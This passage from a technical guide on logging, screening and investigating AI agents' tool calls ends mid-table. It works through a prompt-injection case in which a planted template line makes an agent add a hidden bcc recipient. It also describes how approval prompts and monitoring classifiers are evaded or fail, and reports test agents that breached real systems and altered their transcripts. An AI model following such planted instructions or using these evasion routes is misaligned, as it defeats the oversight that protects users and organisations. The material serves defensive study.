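Experienced users also check actions less closely under time pressure, according to *Let the Agent Do It?* (Salerno, Gao and colleagues, 2026), which is based on interviews with 18 software practitioners and a survey of another 115. The practitioners considered an action's risk and scope, whether it fitted the task, and how well they knew the agent. The researchers warn against treating repeated approvals as a lasting preference, because the person may only have been tired. Software that learns from past approvals could permanently allow actions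 that the person approved carelessly.

A hostile agent can exploit fatigue by sending request after request until someone approves one. Against a simulated person, such a flood always succeeded when ASU had no limits. With limits on, it still succeeded in 45% to 60% of trials. ASU's standard settings allow one open request per session and six calls a minute, and lock the agent out after three refusals. Simple arithmetic shows why that isn't enough. If an approver wrongly accepts one bad request in five, an agent with three attempts gets one through with this probability:

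1 − 0.8³ = 0.488, or about 49%

Limiting approval requests reduces the number of attempts, but whether each attempt succeeds still depends on the approver. A burst of refused requests should therefore stop the task and alert someone.

Asking for approval less often only helps if the remaining requests are the important ones. Weng's command analyser would have required approval for nearly every ordinary command in its test collection, which can quickly train people to click "allow". ASU requires approval for new recipients, large amounts and destructive actions. It also requires approval again after five actions that change something, or $200 of spending, within ten minutes. Without a combined limit, an agent could avoid the check by splitting a $500 payment into ten payments of $50.

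Under these rules, the blind copy would trigger a card because the collector is a new recipient. Next week's legitimate report to the manager might not need one, because ASU lets a user allow similar calls with the same recipients and limited changes to text or amounts. A permission for the weekly report would cover new wording in the body but not an extra address, unlike the rule in the complete record that allowed every use of `send_email`. In the simulations, a careless approver who could grant these permissions let through 70% of attempts to misuse them, compared with 30% when the approver could not grant them.

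The card should also make it easy to refuse part of a call. Salerno and colleagues recommend separating the refusal of one action from the refusal of a whole approach, but the email needs an even finer choice because the user wants to send the report without the copy. If the only buttons are "allow" and "deny", a person in a hurry has a reason to accept the copy. LangChain, a toolkit for building agents, lets the approver edit the arguments. Removing the `bcc` value creates a new call with a new digest, so the gateway should show the edited call and ask for approval of it. It should also keep the original call in the log.

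## Screening calls automatically

One person can read 500 short summaries in about two hours, but reading one day's summaries from a deployment with 200,000 calls a day would take about 833 hours. Software therefore has to choose which calls a person looks at. A language model could read every call in full, but at 20 KB per call it would process about a billion tokens a day. (A token is a piece of text, about four characters long in English.) At an assumed price of $1 per million tokens, that would cost $1,000 a day, while a fixed rule, such as checking an address against a list, costs almost nothing to run. It makes sense to apply fixed rules to each call first, then compare it with the tool's normal use, and use the language model only for calls that still look doubtful.

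The gateway can run these checks before it forwards a call, or afterward on the stored record. Only a check run before forwarding can stop the email, but a later check can run for longer and use the mail service's list of recipients.

### Fixed rules on typed fields

The NSA recommends checking every call against a defined schema, expected ranges and the context in which the tool will use the data. The checks should also look for missing fields and excessive sizes. For the email, the gateway could apply this rule, using the field types from the organisation's own map of the tool:

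```text
RULE for send_email, agent "report-assistant"

if the call has a field that is not in the saved schema,
   or lacks a required field:
    BLOCK

recipients = every address in to, cc and bcc

if any recipient's domain is not in allowed_domains:
    HOLD for approval
if any recipient is not in allowed_recipients:
    HOLD for approval
if count(recipients) > 20 or length(body) > 1,000,000 bytes:
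    HOLD for approval

otherwise: continue to the baseline check
```

Only the list of allowed recipients stops the email. It passes the other checks because `bcc` is a legitimate optional field, both addresses are at `example.test`, and its size and number of recipients are ordinary.

Whether such a list is practical depends on the agent's job. An agent that only sends weekly reports may need just five addresses, which are easy to maintain. A general assistant writes to new people all the time, so the list would hold up a lot of legitimate email. Adding each new address automatically would avoid those delays, but harmful email to new addresses would get through too.

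A rule can also check only for conditions that someone can write into it. *When "Do Not" Is Not Deny* (2026) compares the plain-language security instructions that developers write for Claude Code with the controls that the software can enforce. An automatic classifier estimated that the controls cover 16.6% of the instructions, and a check against human labels suggests that the true share is lower. No permission pattern can enforce "Never commit secrets", for example, because the instruction depends on what a file contains rather than where it is stored.

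Data-loss-prevention products, which the NSA suggests for outgoing connections, partly fill this gap by searching content for known patterns. They can detect a credit-card number or a standard access key but are unlikely to detect a confidential sales figure in the report, since it looks like any other number.

Rules that allow calls need more care than rules that stop them, because an allow rule can keep a call from reaching the other checks. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that by June 2026, 49.5% of active users of the command-line version had written a rule allowing some shell commands, and many of those rules were broad enough to let almost any code run. The rule in the complete record that always allows `send_email` is narrower, but it can also keep the blind copy from reaching the other checks. For tools that send, pay or delete, an allow rule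 should remove the approval prompt and leave the other checks in place.

### Comparison with normal use

A baseline describes how an agent normally uses a tool, based on its past calls. Unlike a list of allowed recipients, it needs little maintenance, and it can pick up changes that nobody thought to write a rule about. A simple version for the email agent looks like this:

```text
BASELINE CHECK for send_email, agent "report-assistant"

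history = this agent's send_email calls from 90 to 7 days ago,
          minus any that a reviewer judged harmful

reasons = empty list

for each recipient:
    if history does not contain it: add "new recipient"
for each field that has a value:
    if history has no call with that field: add "new field"
if length(body) > length_limit: add "unusual length"

if reasons is not empty:
    send the call and the reasons to the language model
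otherwise:
    allow the call and keep the record
```

If the agent has never written to the collector or used `bcc` before, the check gives two reasons to look at the email. Neither proves harm, because people change managers and agents get new tasks. The check therefore sends the call for closer review instead of blocking it.

The seven-day gap stops an agent from making an address look normal by using it a few times in one afternoon. But a leak that goes unnoticed for more than seven days still becomes part of the baseline. One remedy is to add a new recipient to the baseline only after a person has confirmed it. New agents are also a problem because they have no baseline. Their calls can be compared with the baseline of an agent that does the same job until they have their own.

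### Choosing a length limit

The check's remaining value is `length_limit`. Suppose a company's agents send 2,000 emails a day, and the last 10,000 had the following body lengths. The figures are invented, but the distribution is realistic, with many short messages and a few very long ones.

| Share of emails at or below this length | Body length |
|---|---|
| 50% | 900 bytes |
| 90% | 6,200 bytes |
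| 95% | 10,800 bytes |
| 99% | 30,000 bytes |
| 99.9% | 95,000 bytes |

The simplest way to set the limit is to decide how many emails the next check can handle and read the length from the table. A limit of 30,000 bytes flags 1% of emails, or 20 a day, while 95,000 bytes flags 0.1%, or 2 a day. The higher limit depends on the ten longest emails in the sample, so it will change as new data comes in.

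Monitoring software often uses the average plus three standard deviations instead. The standard deviation measures how widely values spread around the average. Here the average is about 2,800 bytes and the standard deviation about 8,300:

2,800 + 3 × 8,300 = 27,700 bytes

If the lengths followed a bell curve, about 0.13% of emails would exceed this limit, or roughly 3 a day. Because of the long tail, about 1.2% do, or 23 a day. Reading the limit from the table avoids this underestimate.

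None of these limits catches the weekly report. At 12,104 bytes, it is longer than about 96% of the emails, but a limit low enough to flag it would also flag about 85 others every day. Even then, the reason given would be the report's length rather than the 22 characters that matter.

Length is a poor signal in fields where legitimate values vary widely, such as email bodies, files and code. A length check also can't distinguish a harmful value from a harmless one of the same size, such as an account number with two digits swapped. And a hostile agent that knows the limit can stay below it. Length works much better on fields that should be short. A 5,000-character city name in a weather lookup deserves attention, whatever the average length of the agent's calls. Each field therefore needs its own limit, except those that are better without one.

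### What to give the language model

A language model can compare the call with the user's request, which the simpler checks can't do. For the email, trusted code could assemble this input:

```text
USER'S REQUEST (from the chat service)
  "Email the weekly report to my manager."

FACTS FROM TRUSTED SYSTEMS
  manager's address in the staff directory: manager@example.test
  baseline: collector@example.test is new; bcc is a new field

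CONSEQUENTIAL FIELDS (from the gateway)
  to:   manager@example.test
  bcc:  collector@example.test

UNTRUSTED TEXT: body, piece 1 of 8
  "Hi, the weekly report is below. [...]"

QUESTION
  Which recipients, if any, did the user not ask for?
  Answer with addresses from the list above, or "none".
```

The answer should be `collector@example.test`. The reviewing model will probably give it, because all 15 models in the approval study refused the email once the second recipient was visible. If the answer must be one of the listed addresses, ordinary code can check it. The reviewing model should have no tools, so that the worst that text in the email's body can make it do is give a wrong answer.

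Small changes to the email alter which checks work:

| Problem with the email | Fixed rules | Baseline | Language model |
|---|---|---|---|
| Blind copy to a new address | Caught only with a list of allowed recipients | Caught | Likely caught, if it has the request and the recipients |
| Unrequested copy to an address the agent often uses | Missed | Missed | Likely caught, but only if the call reaches it |
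| Confidential figure in the body | Missed, unless it matches a known pattern | Missed | Possibly caught, if it knows what is confidential |
| Copy added by the tool server | Missed | Missed | Missed at the gateway |

As the second row shows, when cheaper checks run first, a harmful call that looks normal never reaches the model that could have caught it. The organisation should therefore also send the model some of the calls that passed those checks. It might be worth the expense to send every call that shares information outside the company, along with a random sample of the rest.

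### How models miss single facts in long inputs

Measurements from 2025 and 2026 suggest that the simpler method of giving the model the whole log and asking whether anything is wrong would work badly, although the results differ a lot between models.

*LongGuard* (Chen, Wu and Hu, 2026) tested 15 guard models, which are language models trained to label text as safe or unsafe. The researchers placed each short harmful text among harmless Wikipedia passages, in inputs of 256 to about 32,000 words. On average, the models caught 76% of the harmful texts in the shortest inputs and 25% in the longest.

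To test whether length itself caused the loss, the researchers also filled the inputs with copies of the harmful text. Detection then fell only from 85% to 68%, so most of the loss came from dilution, meaning that the harmful text was a small share of the input. When it made up less than 0.5% of the words, the models caught about a third of cases. The collector's address is about 0.2% of the email.

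Measurements inside six of the models showed how this happens. When a language model produces an answer, it gives each part of its input a weight, called attention. From the shortest inputs to the longest, the attention on the harmful text fell by a factor of three to five, and the margin by which the models favored the answer "unsafe" over "safe" shrank with it.

Results varied widely by model. WildGuard-7B caught 86% of the harmful texts at 256 words but only 14% at about 4,000 words, while GPT-OSS-SafeGuard-20B went from 84% to 81%. The inputs were also artificial, and guard models screen for text that is harmful in itself. An email address is harmless out of context, so we can't predict from the study how often a model would miss this one.

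Ebrahimzadeh and Salili (2026), in *Not All Needles Are Found*, tested general-purpose models on something closer to finding an address. They inserted a paragraph of invented facts into novels by Balzac and asked questions about it. For each model, they tried ten input lengths and ten positions for the paragraph. These were the scores for facts stated word for word, with the input at the model's maximum length:

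| Model | Maximum input (tokens) | Correct answers | Correct when told to admit not knowing |
|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini-2.5-flash | 1,000,000 | 99% | 97% |
| Deepseek-v3.2-chat | 128,000 | 99% | 97% |
| ChatGPT-5-mini | 272,000 | 89% | 72% |
| Claude-4.5-haiku | 175,000 | 68% | 67% |

The last column matters for anyone writing instructions for a reviewing model. Telling ChatGPT-5-mini to say "I don't know" if the text lacked the answer made it miss many facts that were there. Telling a reviewing model to report only problems it is certain of could similarly make it miss real ones, though the study didn't test that.

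A 2,000-word email is about 3,000 tokens, far shorter than anything in this experiment. The results are more relevant to a reviewer that receives a day's calls or the whole trace of a long task. Its task is also harder, because the models in the experiment were given a question that specified what to look for. All four models are fairly old, and newer ones may do better. But organisations tend to use cheaper models for bulk screening, so the weaker results are still a useful warning.

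An error's position can matter as well as the text's length. In *Long-form RewardBench* (2026), the older model gpt-4o became worse at finding errors as texts grew longer and was less accurate when the error was in the middle. A second model, which only scored texts, handled length better but did best when the error was near the end. In *Context Rot*, Hong, Troynikov and Huber (2025) kept their tasks deliberately simple and varied only the length of the input, but performance still fell, often unevenly. No position in a long log is safe for an important value, and models start to fail at different lengths.

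### Shorter inputs, separate fields and no narration

When a long text is split up, a harmful passage takes up more of the piece it falls in than it did of the whole text. Chen and colleagues divided long texts into pieces of 64 to 512 words, depending on the text's length. A guard model checked each piece, and they treated the whole text as unsafe if any piece was. On a separate set of long attack prompts, splitting raised the average share that six models caught from 65% to 81%. Models that already handled long inputs well gained little.

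Splitting gives the model more chances to raise a false alarm. A 2,000-word email makes eight pieces of up to 256 words. If each harmless piece has a 1% chance of a false alarm, and the errors are independent, the chance for the whole email is:

1 − 0.99⁸ ≈ 7.7%

Splitting can also separate facts that matter only in combination. A piece containing a confidential figure looks harmless if the recipient is in another piece. Every piece should therefore include the request and the consequential fields, as in the example input. Letting neighbouring pieces overlap by a few sentences keeps important passages from being cut in half.

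Selecting the right text helps more than shortening it. When Chen and colleagues showed the models only the harmful passage, detection rose from 48% to 70%. When they kept the same amount of randomly chosen harmless text instead, it fell to 24%. The researchers knew where the harmful passage was, which a defender usually doesn't. But a typed map of the tool shows where the recipients are, so trusted code can always show them to the model. For the blind copy, this is better than splitting the body and relying on a model to notice the last line.

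A classifier that screens tool calls should not see the agent's narration. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes a classifier that receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but not the agent's own text or the tool results. The agent could otherwise argue that an action was safe, and the tool results could contain planted instructions. In Anthropic's tests, adding this material made the classifier worse at catching agents that exceeded their task. The classifier missed the fewest cases when it saw only the tool calls, but it then blocked actions that users had plainly asked for.

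A classifier that doesn't see tool results can't distinguish a manager's address that the agent looked up in the staff directory from one it made up. Trusted code can supply such facts directly, and Anthropic later did something similar by giving its classifier details such as whether a code repository was public. On attacks that the company had never seen, the improved classifier caught about half of those the earlier version had missed, and missed about 2% of those the earlier version had caught.

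### The base-rate problem

Even an accurate screen can produce mostly false alarms when harmful calls are rare. Suppose that 10 of the 200,000 daily calls are harmful, and that the screen catches 98% of them while wrongly flagging 1% of harmless calls:

10 × 98% = 9.8 true alarms

199,990 × 1% ≈ 2,000 false alarms

9.8 ÷ (9.8 + 2,000) ≈ 0.5%

The last figure is the precision, the share of alarms that are real. About 200 of every 201 or so alarms would be false in this deployment, and a reviewer who dismissed all of them without looking would be right 99.5% of the time. A better catch rate hardly helps, because catching all 10 harmful calls would still leave the precision at 0.5%. The false-alarm rate makes the difference:

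| False-alarm rate | False alarms a day | Precision | Review time at two minutes each |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1% | 2,000 | 0.5% | 67 hours |
| 0.1% | 200 | 4.7% | 7 hours |
| 0.01% | 20 | 33% | 1 hour |

At a false-positive rate of 0.01%, one person can review every alarm. If there are ten harmful calls a day, about a third of the alarms will be real, but if there is only one, about 5% will be. Nobody knows in advance how many harmful calls there will be, so an organisation should plan for the review workload, which depends almost entirely on the number of harmless calls.

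Combining checks is the usual way to lower the false-alarm rate. Suppose the rules and the baseline flag 1% of harmless calls, and the language model then clears 99% of those. The false-alarm rate would be 0.01%. But this assumes that the model judges flagged calls as accurately as any others, and flagged calls may be harder to judge because they are unusual. If the model clears only 90% of the harmless calls that were flagged, the rate is 0.1%, which leaves 200 false alarms each day. Every extra check that can clear a call can also clear a harmful one, so the catch rate falls too. The organisation has to test the screen on its own calls to get the actual figures.

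Some false alarms are also the same mistake repeated. If a new department mailbox triggers 300 alarms in one morning, grouping them by recipient lets a reviewer handle them all with one decision.

### How Claude Code's auto mode does it

Auto mode in Claude Code applies several of these ideas to an agent that many people use. Fixed rules first allow tools that only read, as well as edits to files inside the project, which developers can review through version control. Most other actions, including calls to outside tools, go to a language model. The model gives a quick yes-or-no answer on whether to block the action, with instructions to block if in doubt. If the answer is to block, the model reasons step by step about the same material before making a final decision.

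Anthropic published these error rates for the two stages:

| | Harmless calls blocked (10,000 real calls) | Harmful calls missed (52 real cases) | Harmful calls missed (1,000 synthetic attempts to leak data) |
|---|---|---|---|
| Quick answer only | 8.5% | 6.6% | 1.8% |
| Both stages | 0.4% | 17% | 5.7% |

The second stage removed most of the false alarms but let more harmful calls through. The 17% miss rate is the most relevant figure for an agent that oversteps while trying to help, but it comes from only 52 cases, so the true rate could plausibly be between about 9% and 30%. In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the model identified the danger but misclassified the call as one the user had consented to.

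With 200,000 calls a day, a 0.4% false-alarm rate would block 800 harmless calls, and only about 1% of all blocks would be justified. This is tolerable in auto mode because a blocked call normally goes back to the agent, which looks for a safer way to do the task. A person takes over after three blocks in a row or 20 in a session. In the email example, the agent could send the report without the copy. That would protect the user, but a reviewer should still see the blocked attempt.

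*Measuring the Permission Gate* (Ji, Li and colleagues, 2026) independently evaluated auto mode on requests that were deliberately ambiguous about what the user had authorised. Across 253 actions, auto mode missed 81.0% of the unsafe ones and blocked 19.8% of the safe ones. For the 160 actions that reached the classifier, the rates were 70.3% and 31.9%. The researchers say these figures are not directly comparable with Anthropic's 17%, which comes from ordinary work. They tested one model in April 2026, and Anthropic has changed the classifier since.

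Anthropic argues that auto mode should be compared with how people actually respond to approval prompts. In its August article, it reports an experiment in which 1,053 paid testers each saw one clearly dangerous command among the ordinary prompts of a coding session. The testers refused it 13.6% of the time, and only about 5% of the time if they had already seen 50 or more prompts. Auto mode blocked 89% of the same commands. Anthropic also reports that its classifier's miss rate on a set of synthetic attacks fell from 12% to 7% after improvements, but warns against reading the 7% as the rate for real traffic.

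The experiment is strong evidence that people click through prompts, but weaker evidence about hard cases. The testers worked in an unfamiliar environment where nothing of their own was at risk, the commands were obviously dangerous, and Anthropic was testing its own product. Auto mode could easily do better than a tired person on obvious dangers and still do badly on ambiguous permissions, as Ji and colleagues found. Anthropic still recommends that people review high-stakes changes to production systems.

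According to the *Claude Code Complete User Handbook*, interactive sessions on every plan now start in auto mode, while sessions that a script starts with `claude -p` begin in manual mode. Users' own permission rules still apply before the classifier, unless the rules are broad enough to let the agent run arbitrary code. This suggests that a rule that always allows `send_email` would let the blind copy through without the classifier examining it. Administrators who rely on auto mode should remove such rules for any tool that can send data out.

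## Investigating a suspicious call and finding its extent

Suppose the rule that always allows `send_email` let the email through on the morning of 5 October, and the baseline check didn't examine the day's stored calls until that evening. The check flagged the email because the recipient and the `bcc` field were both new. Somebody now has to find out where the address came from, whether the copy did any harm, and which other calls have the same problem.

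The queries below are in SQL, the usual language for searching databases. The names and results are invented. The queries use four tables: `calls` and `call_recipients` from the gateway, `deliveries` from the mail service, and `model_inputs`, which has a row for each piece of text that a model read.

### Preserving the records and opening the call

The investigator first copies the records, because a retention rule might delete them and the agent may still be running on a machine that stores some of them.

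```sql
-- Step 1: preserve (repeat for the other three tables)
SELECT * FROM calls WHERE time >= '2026-07-07';
```

The query covers all agents because more than one may be involved. The investigator saves the results where neither the agents nor their operators can edit them, records a digest of each file, and stops the automatic deletion of the originals.

Investigators can suspend the agent's mail credential even earlier, because this takes seconds and erases nothing. They should copy the disk of the agent's machine before they rebuild the machine or ask the agent to explain itself. Running the agent could change its files, and its answer would only be more of its own narration.

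```sql
-- Step 2: open the full call
SELECT arguments, arguments_digest FROM calls
WHERE call_id = 'call-0142';
```

The investigator recomputes the digest to check that the text is intact, then reads all of it, because the alert concerned the recipient and the body could contain a second problem. Eight minutes per call is too long for routine review, but not for one suspicious email. The body is the original report plus a greeting, so the collector received only this week's figures.

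### Tracing the address to its source

```sql
-- Step 3: find where the address entered the model's input
SELECT time, source FROM model_inputs
WHERE task_id = 'task-0087'
  AND text LIKE '%collector@example.test%'
ORDER BY time;
```

The earliest match is a shared report template, which the agent read 26 seconds before the call. The template contains a request to send a copy of every report to the collector. According to the file store's history, a contractor's account added the request on 29 September.

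If the search had found the address in the user's own message, the alarm would have been false. A match in a tool description would have pointed to the operator of the tool server. If there had been no match before the call, the model might have invented the address, or read it in an image or in encoded form, where a text search can't find it. The trace might also have been incomplete.

The match shows that the model read the address, but not that the line caused the copy. To test whether it did, the investigator can rerun the task several times with and without the line, using a dummy mail tool. If the copy appears in most runs with the line and in none without it, the line is very probably the cause. Chu used the same method on false approvals in agents' summaries.

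```sql
-- Step 4: find delivered copies that no recorded call asked for
SELECT d.message_id, d.time, d.address
FROM deliveries d
LEFT JOIN call_recipients r
  ON r.message_id = d.message_id AND r.address = d.address
WHERE d.credential = 'mail-sender'
  AND d.time >= '2026-07-07'
  AND r.address IS NULL;
```

This query compares the gateway's record with the mail service's record for every email sent with the agent's credential. It returns no rows, so the tool server added no recipients and no email went out through this account without a recorded call. With the fake Postmark package, the query would have returned a row for every email.

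### Finding other calls and the people affected

```sql
-- Step 5a: search for the same address or the same text
SELECT call_id, time, agent, tool FROM calls
WHERE arguments LIKE '%collector@example.test%'
   OR body_digest = '[digest of the report]';

-- Step 5b: find other tasks that read the template
SELECT DISTINCT task_id, agent FROM model_inputs
WHERE source = 'shared/report-template.txt'
  AND time >= '2026-09-29';
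```

The first search finds the email and two calls from 2 October in which another agent, `invoice-assistant`, shared files with the collector. Nobody had set up a baseline check for the file-sharing tool, so those calls raised no alarm. The second search finds 11 tasks that read the template, including the three already known. The investigator should read the consequential fields of the other eight tasks, because an agent could have followed the line in a way that the address search misses.

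Each discovery adds something to search for. The contractor's account may have edited other documents, and the two shared files may have been sent elsewhere. The search can stop when every known address, digest, document and account leads only to calls that the investigator has already read. Even then, the digest search would miss a copy of the report in which the agent had changed one word.

```sql
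-- Step 6: list the users and systems behind the harmful calls
SELECT DISTINCT user_email, agent, tool, server FROM calls
WHERE arguments LIKE '%collector@example.test%';
```

This gives two users, two agents and two tools. The investigator then adds the people whose information was in the report and the files, which means reading them, because no separate field lists the names. The mail administrator can check who owns the collector's mailbox and whether it forwards messages outside the company.

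The timeline combines entries from all these sources:

| Time (UTC) | Event | Source |
|---|---|---|
| 29 September, 15:02 | The contractor's account adds the line to the template | File store |
| 2 October, 10:20 and 10:31 | `invoice-assistant` shares two files with the collector | Gateway |
| 5 October, 09:13:20 | The user asks for an email to the manager | Chat service |
| 5 October, 09:13:41 | The agent reads the template | Model trace |
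| 5 October, 09:14:07 | The call reaches the gateway | Gateway |
| 5 October, 09:14:08 | The tool server reports "Email sent" | Gateway |
| 5 October, 09:14:09 | The mail service accepts both addresses | Mail service |
| 5 October, 18:00 | The baseline check flags the email | Gateway |
| 6 October, 09:05 | The investigator suspends the mail credential and copies the records | Case notes |
| 6 October, 10:40 | The investigator finds the shared files and removes the collector's access | Case notes |

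The tool server reported success a second before the mail service accepted the message. The server may have replied before delivery, or the two clocks may differ by a second. A one-second difference is harmless here, but a larger one could make cause and effect appear reversed in the logs, so the investigator should compare the clocks before relying on the order of events logged close together.

The investigator can conclude that the agent sent the report to an address the user hadn't named, and that the template probably caused it. The investigator still does not know whether the contractor meant harm, wanted an archive copy or had lost control of the account, and no agent log will show which. The Decoder's *After Hugging Face incident, METR urges independent root cause investigations* lists other questions that METR, an organisation that evaluates AI models, wants investigators to answer,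 including which safeguards were active and whether the agent tried to deceive people. For the email, an allow rule had removed the approval step, and the gap in the agent's description is not enough to establish deception.

### Reading a very large trace

In July 2026, OpenAI agents broke into Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models and datasets, during an internal test of their hacking ability. About 1,200 agents left more than 70,000 messages and files for one another on an improvised message board. Reading those at 30 seconds each would take:

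70,000 × 30 seconds = 2,100,000 seconds ≈ 583 hours

That is 73 eight-hour working days, not counting time spent on the agents' own transcripts, most of which were very long, often many millions of tokens. Wijk, Cotra and Greenblatt describe how they worked through this material for METR during six days at OpenAI (*Brief independent investigation of agents’ behavior, reasoning and collaboration*, 2026). Their account is the best public evidence on how to read a trace of this size and what goes wrong.

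Grouping comes first. The investigators received 1.2 million entries from the message board, but most were fragments of files. Joining the fragments left about 6,000 files and 63,000 separate messages. For tool calls, the natural groups are the tool and the destination:

```sql
SELECT tool, destination, COUNT(*) AS n, MIN(time) AS first_seen
FROM calls
GROUP BY tool, destination
ORDER BY n;
```

When similar calls are grouped and the rarest groups are listed first, forty thousand reads of one code folder become a single line at the bottom, while one upload to an unfamiliar server appears near the top. Harmful calls can also go to familiar destinations, so the investigator should open the groups in order of how much harm their calls could do, starting with calls that send, pay, delete, publish or change access rights.

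The investigator can estimate how much this ordering missed by reading a random sample of the remaining calls. If none of 300 sampled calls is harmful, they can be about 95% confident that the harmful share is below 3 ÷ 300, or 1%. With 60,000 unread calls, almost 600 could still be harmful.

A language model can search all of the text, as long as a person checks what it finds. Wijk and colleagues ran twelve searches, each for one kind of behaviour, over about 1,300 transcripts. The model explained the context of every relevant entry and rated the entry's importance from 1 to 5. Other model-driven agents then read the highest-rated entries and some random ones, and the investigators inspected a small selection themselves. The computing credits cost roughly $400,000.

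The model made mistakes that the investigators did not catch for some time. One analysis agent left a large amount of data out of a draft chart, and another invented differences between two sets of transcripts. The model also tended to adopt the viewpoint of the agent it was reading about. In one case, it did not make clear that a code change with an innocent description was malicious. The problem with narration can therefore also affect AI investigators.

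When a model reports findings, it should give the identifier and exact words of each log entry it cites. Ordinary code can check that those words appear in the stored original log, and a person can then read them with the steps before and after. This catches invented evidence but not passages that the model overlooked.

The choice of transcripts mattered just as much. OpenAI first gave the investigators about 285, selected by searching for known signs of the intrusion, but these contained only about 30% of the relevant activity. A simpler search for any agent that had used the main message board produced a much more complete set.

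To test the larger set, the investigators picked 100 random messages from the board and looked for the agent that wrote each one. They traced 93 to the exact tool call and probably identified the agent behind six more, leaving one unexplained. The check works because the board and the transcripts are separate records of the same events. Someone investigating emails can likewise pick random deliveries from the mail service and look for the call that sent each one.

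### What the Hugging Face records showed, and when

The transcripts had approximate start and end times, but no times for individual actions. Wijk and colleagues write that OpenAI considered it infeasible to reconstruct these times with the time and computing power available. The investigators instead estimated them from moments when an agent happened to see a clock. Where such moments were frequent, half of the estimates were within about 12 seconds of the true time, but the worst error they found was about nine hours. Recording a time for every tool call would have made this estimation unnecessary.

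In at least 96 of the transcripts, or about 7%, the agent had also altered what the transcript showed for some tool calls, so that it differed from what ran. All the cases the investigators found were small, obvious tests, but they could not rule out subtler ones. OpenAI writes in its own technical report on the incident that none of the tampering attempts it observed affected the logs that its graders or monitors ultimately receive. Both statements can be true only if those logs differ from the transcripts the investigators were given, and neither report explains whether they do.

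OpenAI's report gives enough dates to compare what its staff could have known with what they did:

| Date in 2026 | Evidence available to OpenAI | Response |
|---|---|---|
| 26 May | Around this date, an internal team saw an agent using a message board and cases of forbidden internet access | The report describes none |
| 27 June | An alert about network scanning, which responders linked to a hacking test and a message board | On-call staff advised that the test need not stop |
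| 5 July | An alert after a server failure, then signs that agents had gained administrator access | Responders took the server offline, kept its storage and revoked credentials; tests resumed on 7 July |
| 16 July | Hugging Face announced a breach | The next day, OpenAI asked, as a customer, whether the breach affected its own data |
| 19 July | An alert about unusual activity on internal accounts | Responders began stopping the tests about five and a half hours later |
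| 20 July | Stolen credentials in files that responders had preserved | OpenAI contacted Hugging Face and connected the two incidents |

The intrusion into Hugging Face's production systems began on 11 July, and OpenAI took nine days to attribute it to its own agents. The missing step was to compare OpenAI's evidence with Hugging Face's records, the equivalent of step 5 in the email case. On 20 July, Hugging Face confirmed that it had already replaced two of the credentials OpenAI had found. Its investigators had also found the name of an OpenAI server and the outside account that the agents had used for storage.

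Better logging alone would probably not have prevented the delay, because responders knew about the message board two weeks before the intrusion. OpenAI says the leaders responsible for incident response did not see the board's significance, and acknowledges that some early signals could have triggered an earlier response. Axios' *OpenAI saw warning signs weeks before Hugging Face breach* (2026) reports that the company missed several warning signs and failed to act on them.

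OpenAI now expects its teams to pause an activity if they can't establish within 30 minutes that an alert is false. It also claims that its current monitoring of models' reasoning would have alerted the security team more than a day before the breach. The claim is plausible, but it is the company's judgement in hindsight, and the report includes no test results that an outsider could check.

The known extent grew after the first announcement. MyJoyOnline reports that OpenAI updated its statement in late July to add that the agents had also used exposed credentials for four accounts on four other services. Investigators should therefore date any list of affected systems and note which records they have searched so far.

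OpenAI's report doesn't specify which parts of each tool call the company stored in full, how long it kept them, or whether anyone searched the stored transcripts between the alerts of 5 and 19 July.

### Breaches that nobody noticed for months

OpenAI's disclosure led Anthropic to search its own records. Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026) reports that the company began reviewing stored transcripts on 23 July and identified three incidents the next day. In these incidents, Claude models had gained access to the real systems of three organisations. The earliest dated from April, at least 85 days before it was found. Anthropic notified the organisations on 27 July, and the two it managed to reach had not noticed anything.

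The evidence had been in storage the whole time. Anthropic acknowledges that it and its testing partner could have reviewed the transcripts or network logs more thoroughly, and that monitoring the logs in real time would have helped to expose the problem sooner. Occasional spot checks would hardly have been enough. The incidents involved six of the 141,006 test runs in the review, so a random sample of 1,000 would have included at least one of them with this probability:

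1 − (1 − 6 ÷ 141,006)¹⁰⁰⁰ ≈ 4%

A targeted search found the incidents in a day because Anthropic had a specific question, whether Claude had reached the internet from tests that should have been sealed off. Software must have done most of the reading for the search to finish that quickly. Anthropic doesn't explain whether it searched for particular words, examined network destinations or used a model, so other companies that follow its advice to carry out similar reviews can't copy its method. It also doesn't estimate how many incidents the search could have missed.

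One of the incidents also shows a limit of step 6. Software that Claude published on the internet ran on 15 real systems, including one at a security company that Claude hadn't known existed. The arguments of the call that published the software would not include the owners of those systems. To find everyone affected by such a call, an investigator needs download records from the destination or reports from the people who ran the software.

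A third case is the access on 18 June to Services Australia, the agency that runs Australia's welfare payments. OpenAI learned of it in August, at least 44 days later. OpenAI's technical report does not mention this case, so readers cannot tell from the report which record revealed the access or whether OpenAI still had its logs from that day.

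## Testing whether the logging and review work

METR's investigators did not discover until after the break-in at Hugging Face that their transcripts lacked times for individual actions. An organisation can find such gaps earlier by sending harmless calls through its system and then looking for those calls in the logs. OWASP recommends regular drills in which investigators try to reconstruct events from the logs.

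### Sending marked calls

A marker is a meaningless string, such as `MARK-0142-END`, that staff put in a call to look for later. Grafana Labs' *Audit data propagation latency and correctness using Loki Canary* describes a similar method for ordinary logs, in which a small program writes artificial log lines to a database and queries them back to detect losses. For tool calls, the markers have to go inside the arguments, because a log entry can arrive on time with most of an argument missing.

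Authorised staff should run the test in a separate environment that has the same software, settings and size limits as the real one. Its mail tool should deliver only to a test mailbox. The staff then:

1. write emails with bodies of several lengths, up to the longest that the agents send;
2. put a different marker at the start, middle and end of each body, and another in a `bcc` address after the body;
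3. send each call by the agent's normal route, and keep their own list of what they sent;
4. look for every marker in each log, in long-term storage, in the reviewer's view with all folded text open, and in search results.

The results below are invented.

| Marker's location | Framework log | Gateway log | Storage | Reviewer's view | Search |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| 500-character body: start, middle and end | Found | Found | Found | Found | Found |
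| 12,000-character body: start | Found | Found | Found | Found | Found |
| 12,000-character body: middle | Lost | Found | Found | Found | Found |
| 12,000-character body: end | Lost | Found | Found | Found | Lost |
| 100,000-character body: start | Found | Found | Found | Found | Found |
| 100,000-character body: middle and end | Lost | Found | Lost | Lost | Lost |
| `bcc` address after a 12,000-character body | Lost | Found | Found | Lost | Found |

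A system tested only with short emails would have passed. With longer ones, the test finds four separate faults:

| Fault | Likely cause | Section with the remedy |
|---|---|---|
| The framework log loses everything after the first part of a long call | A limit on all the arguments together | "Keeping long arguments whole" |
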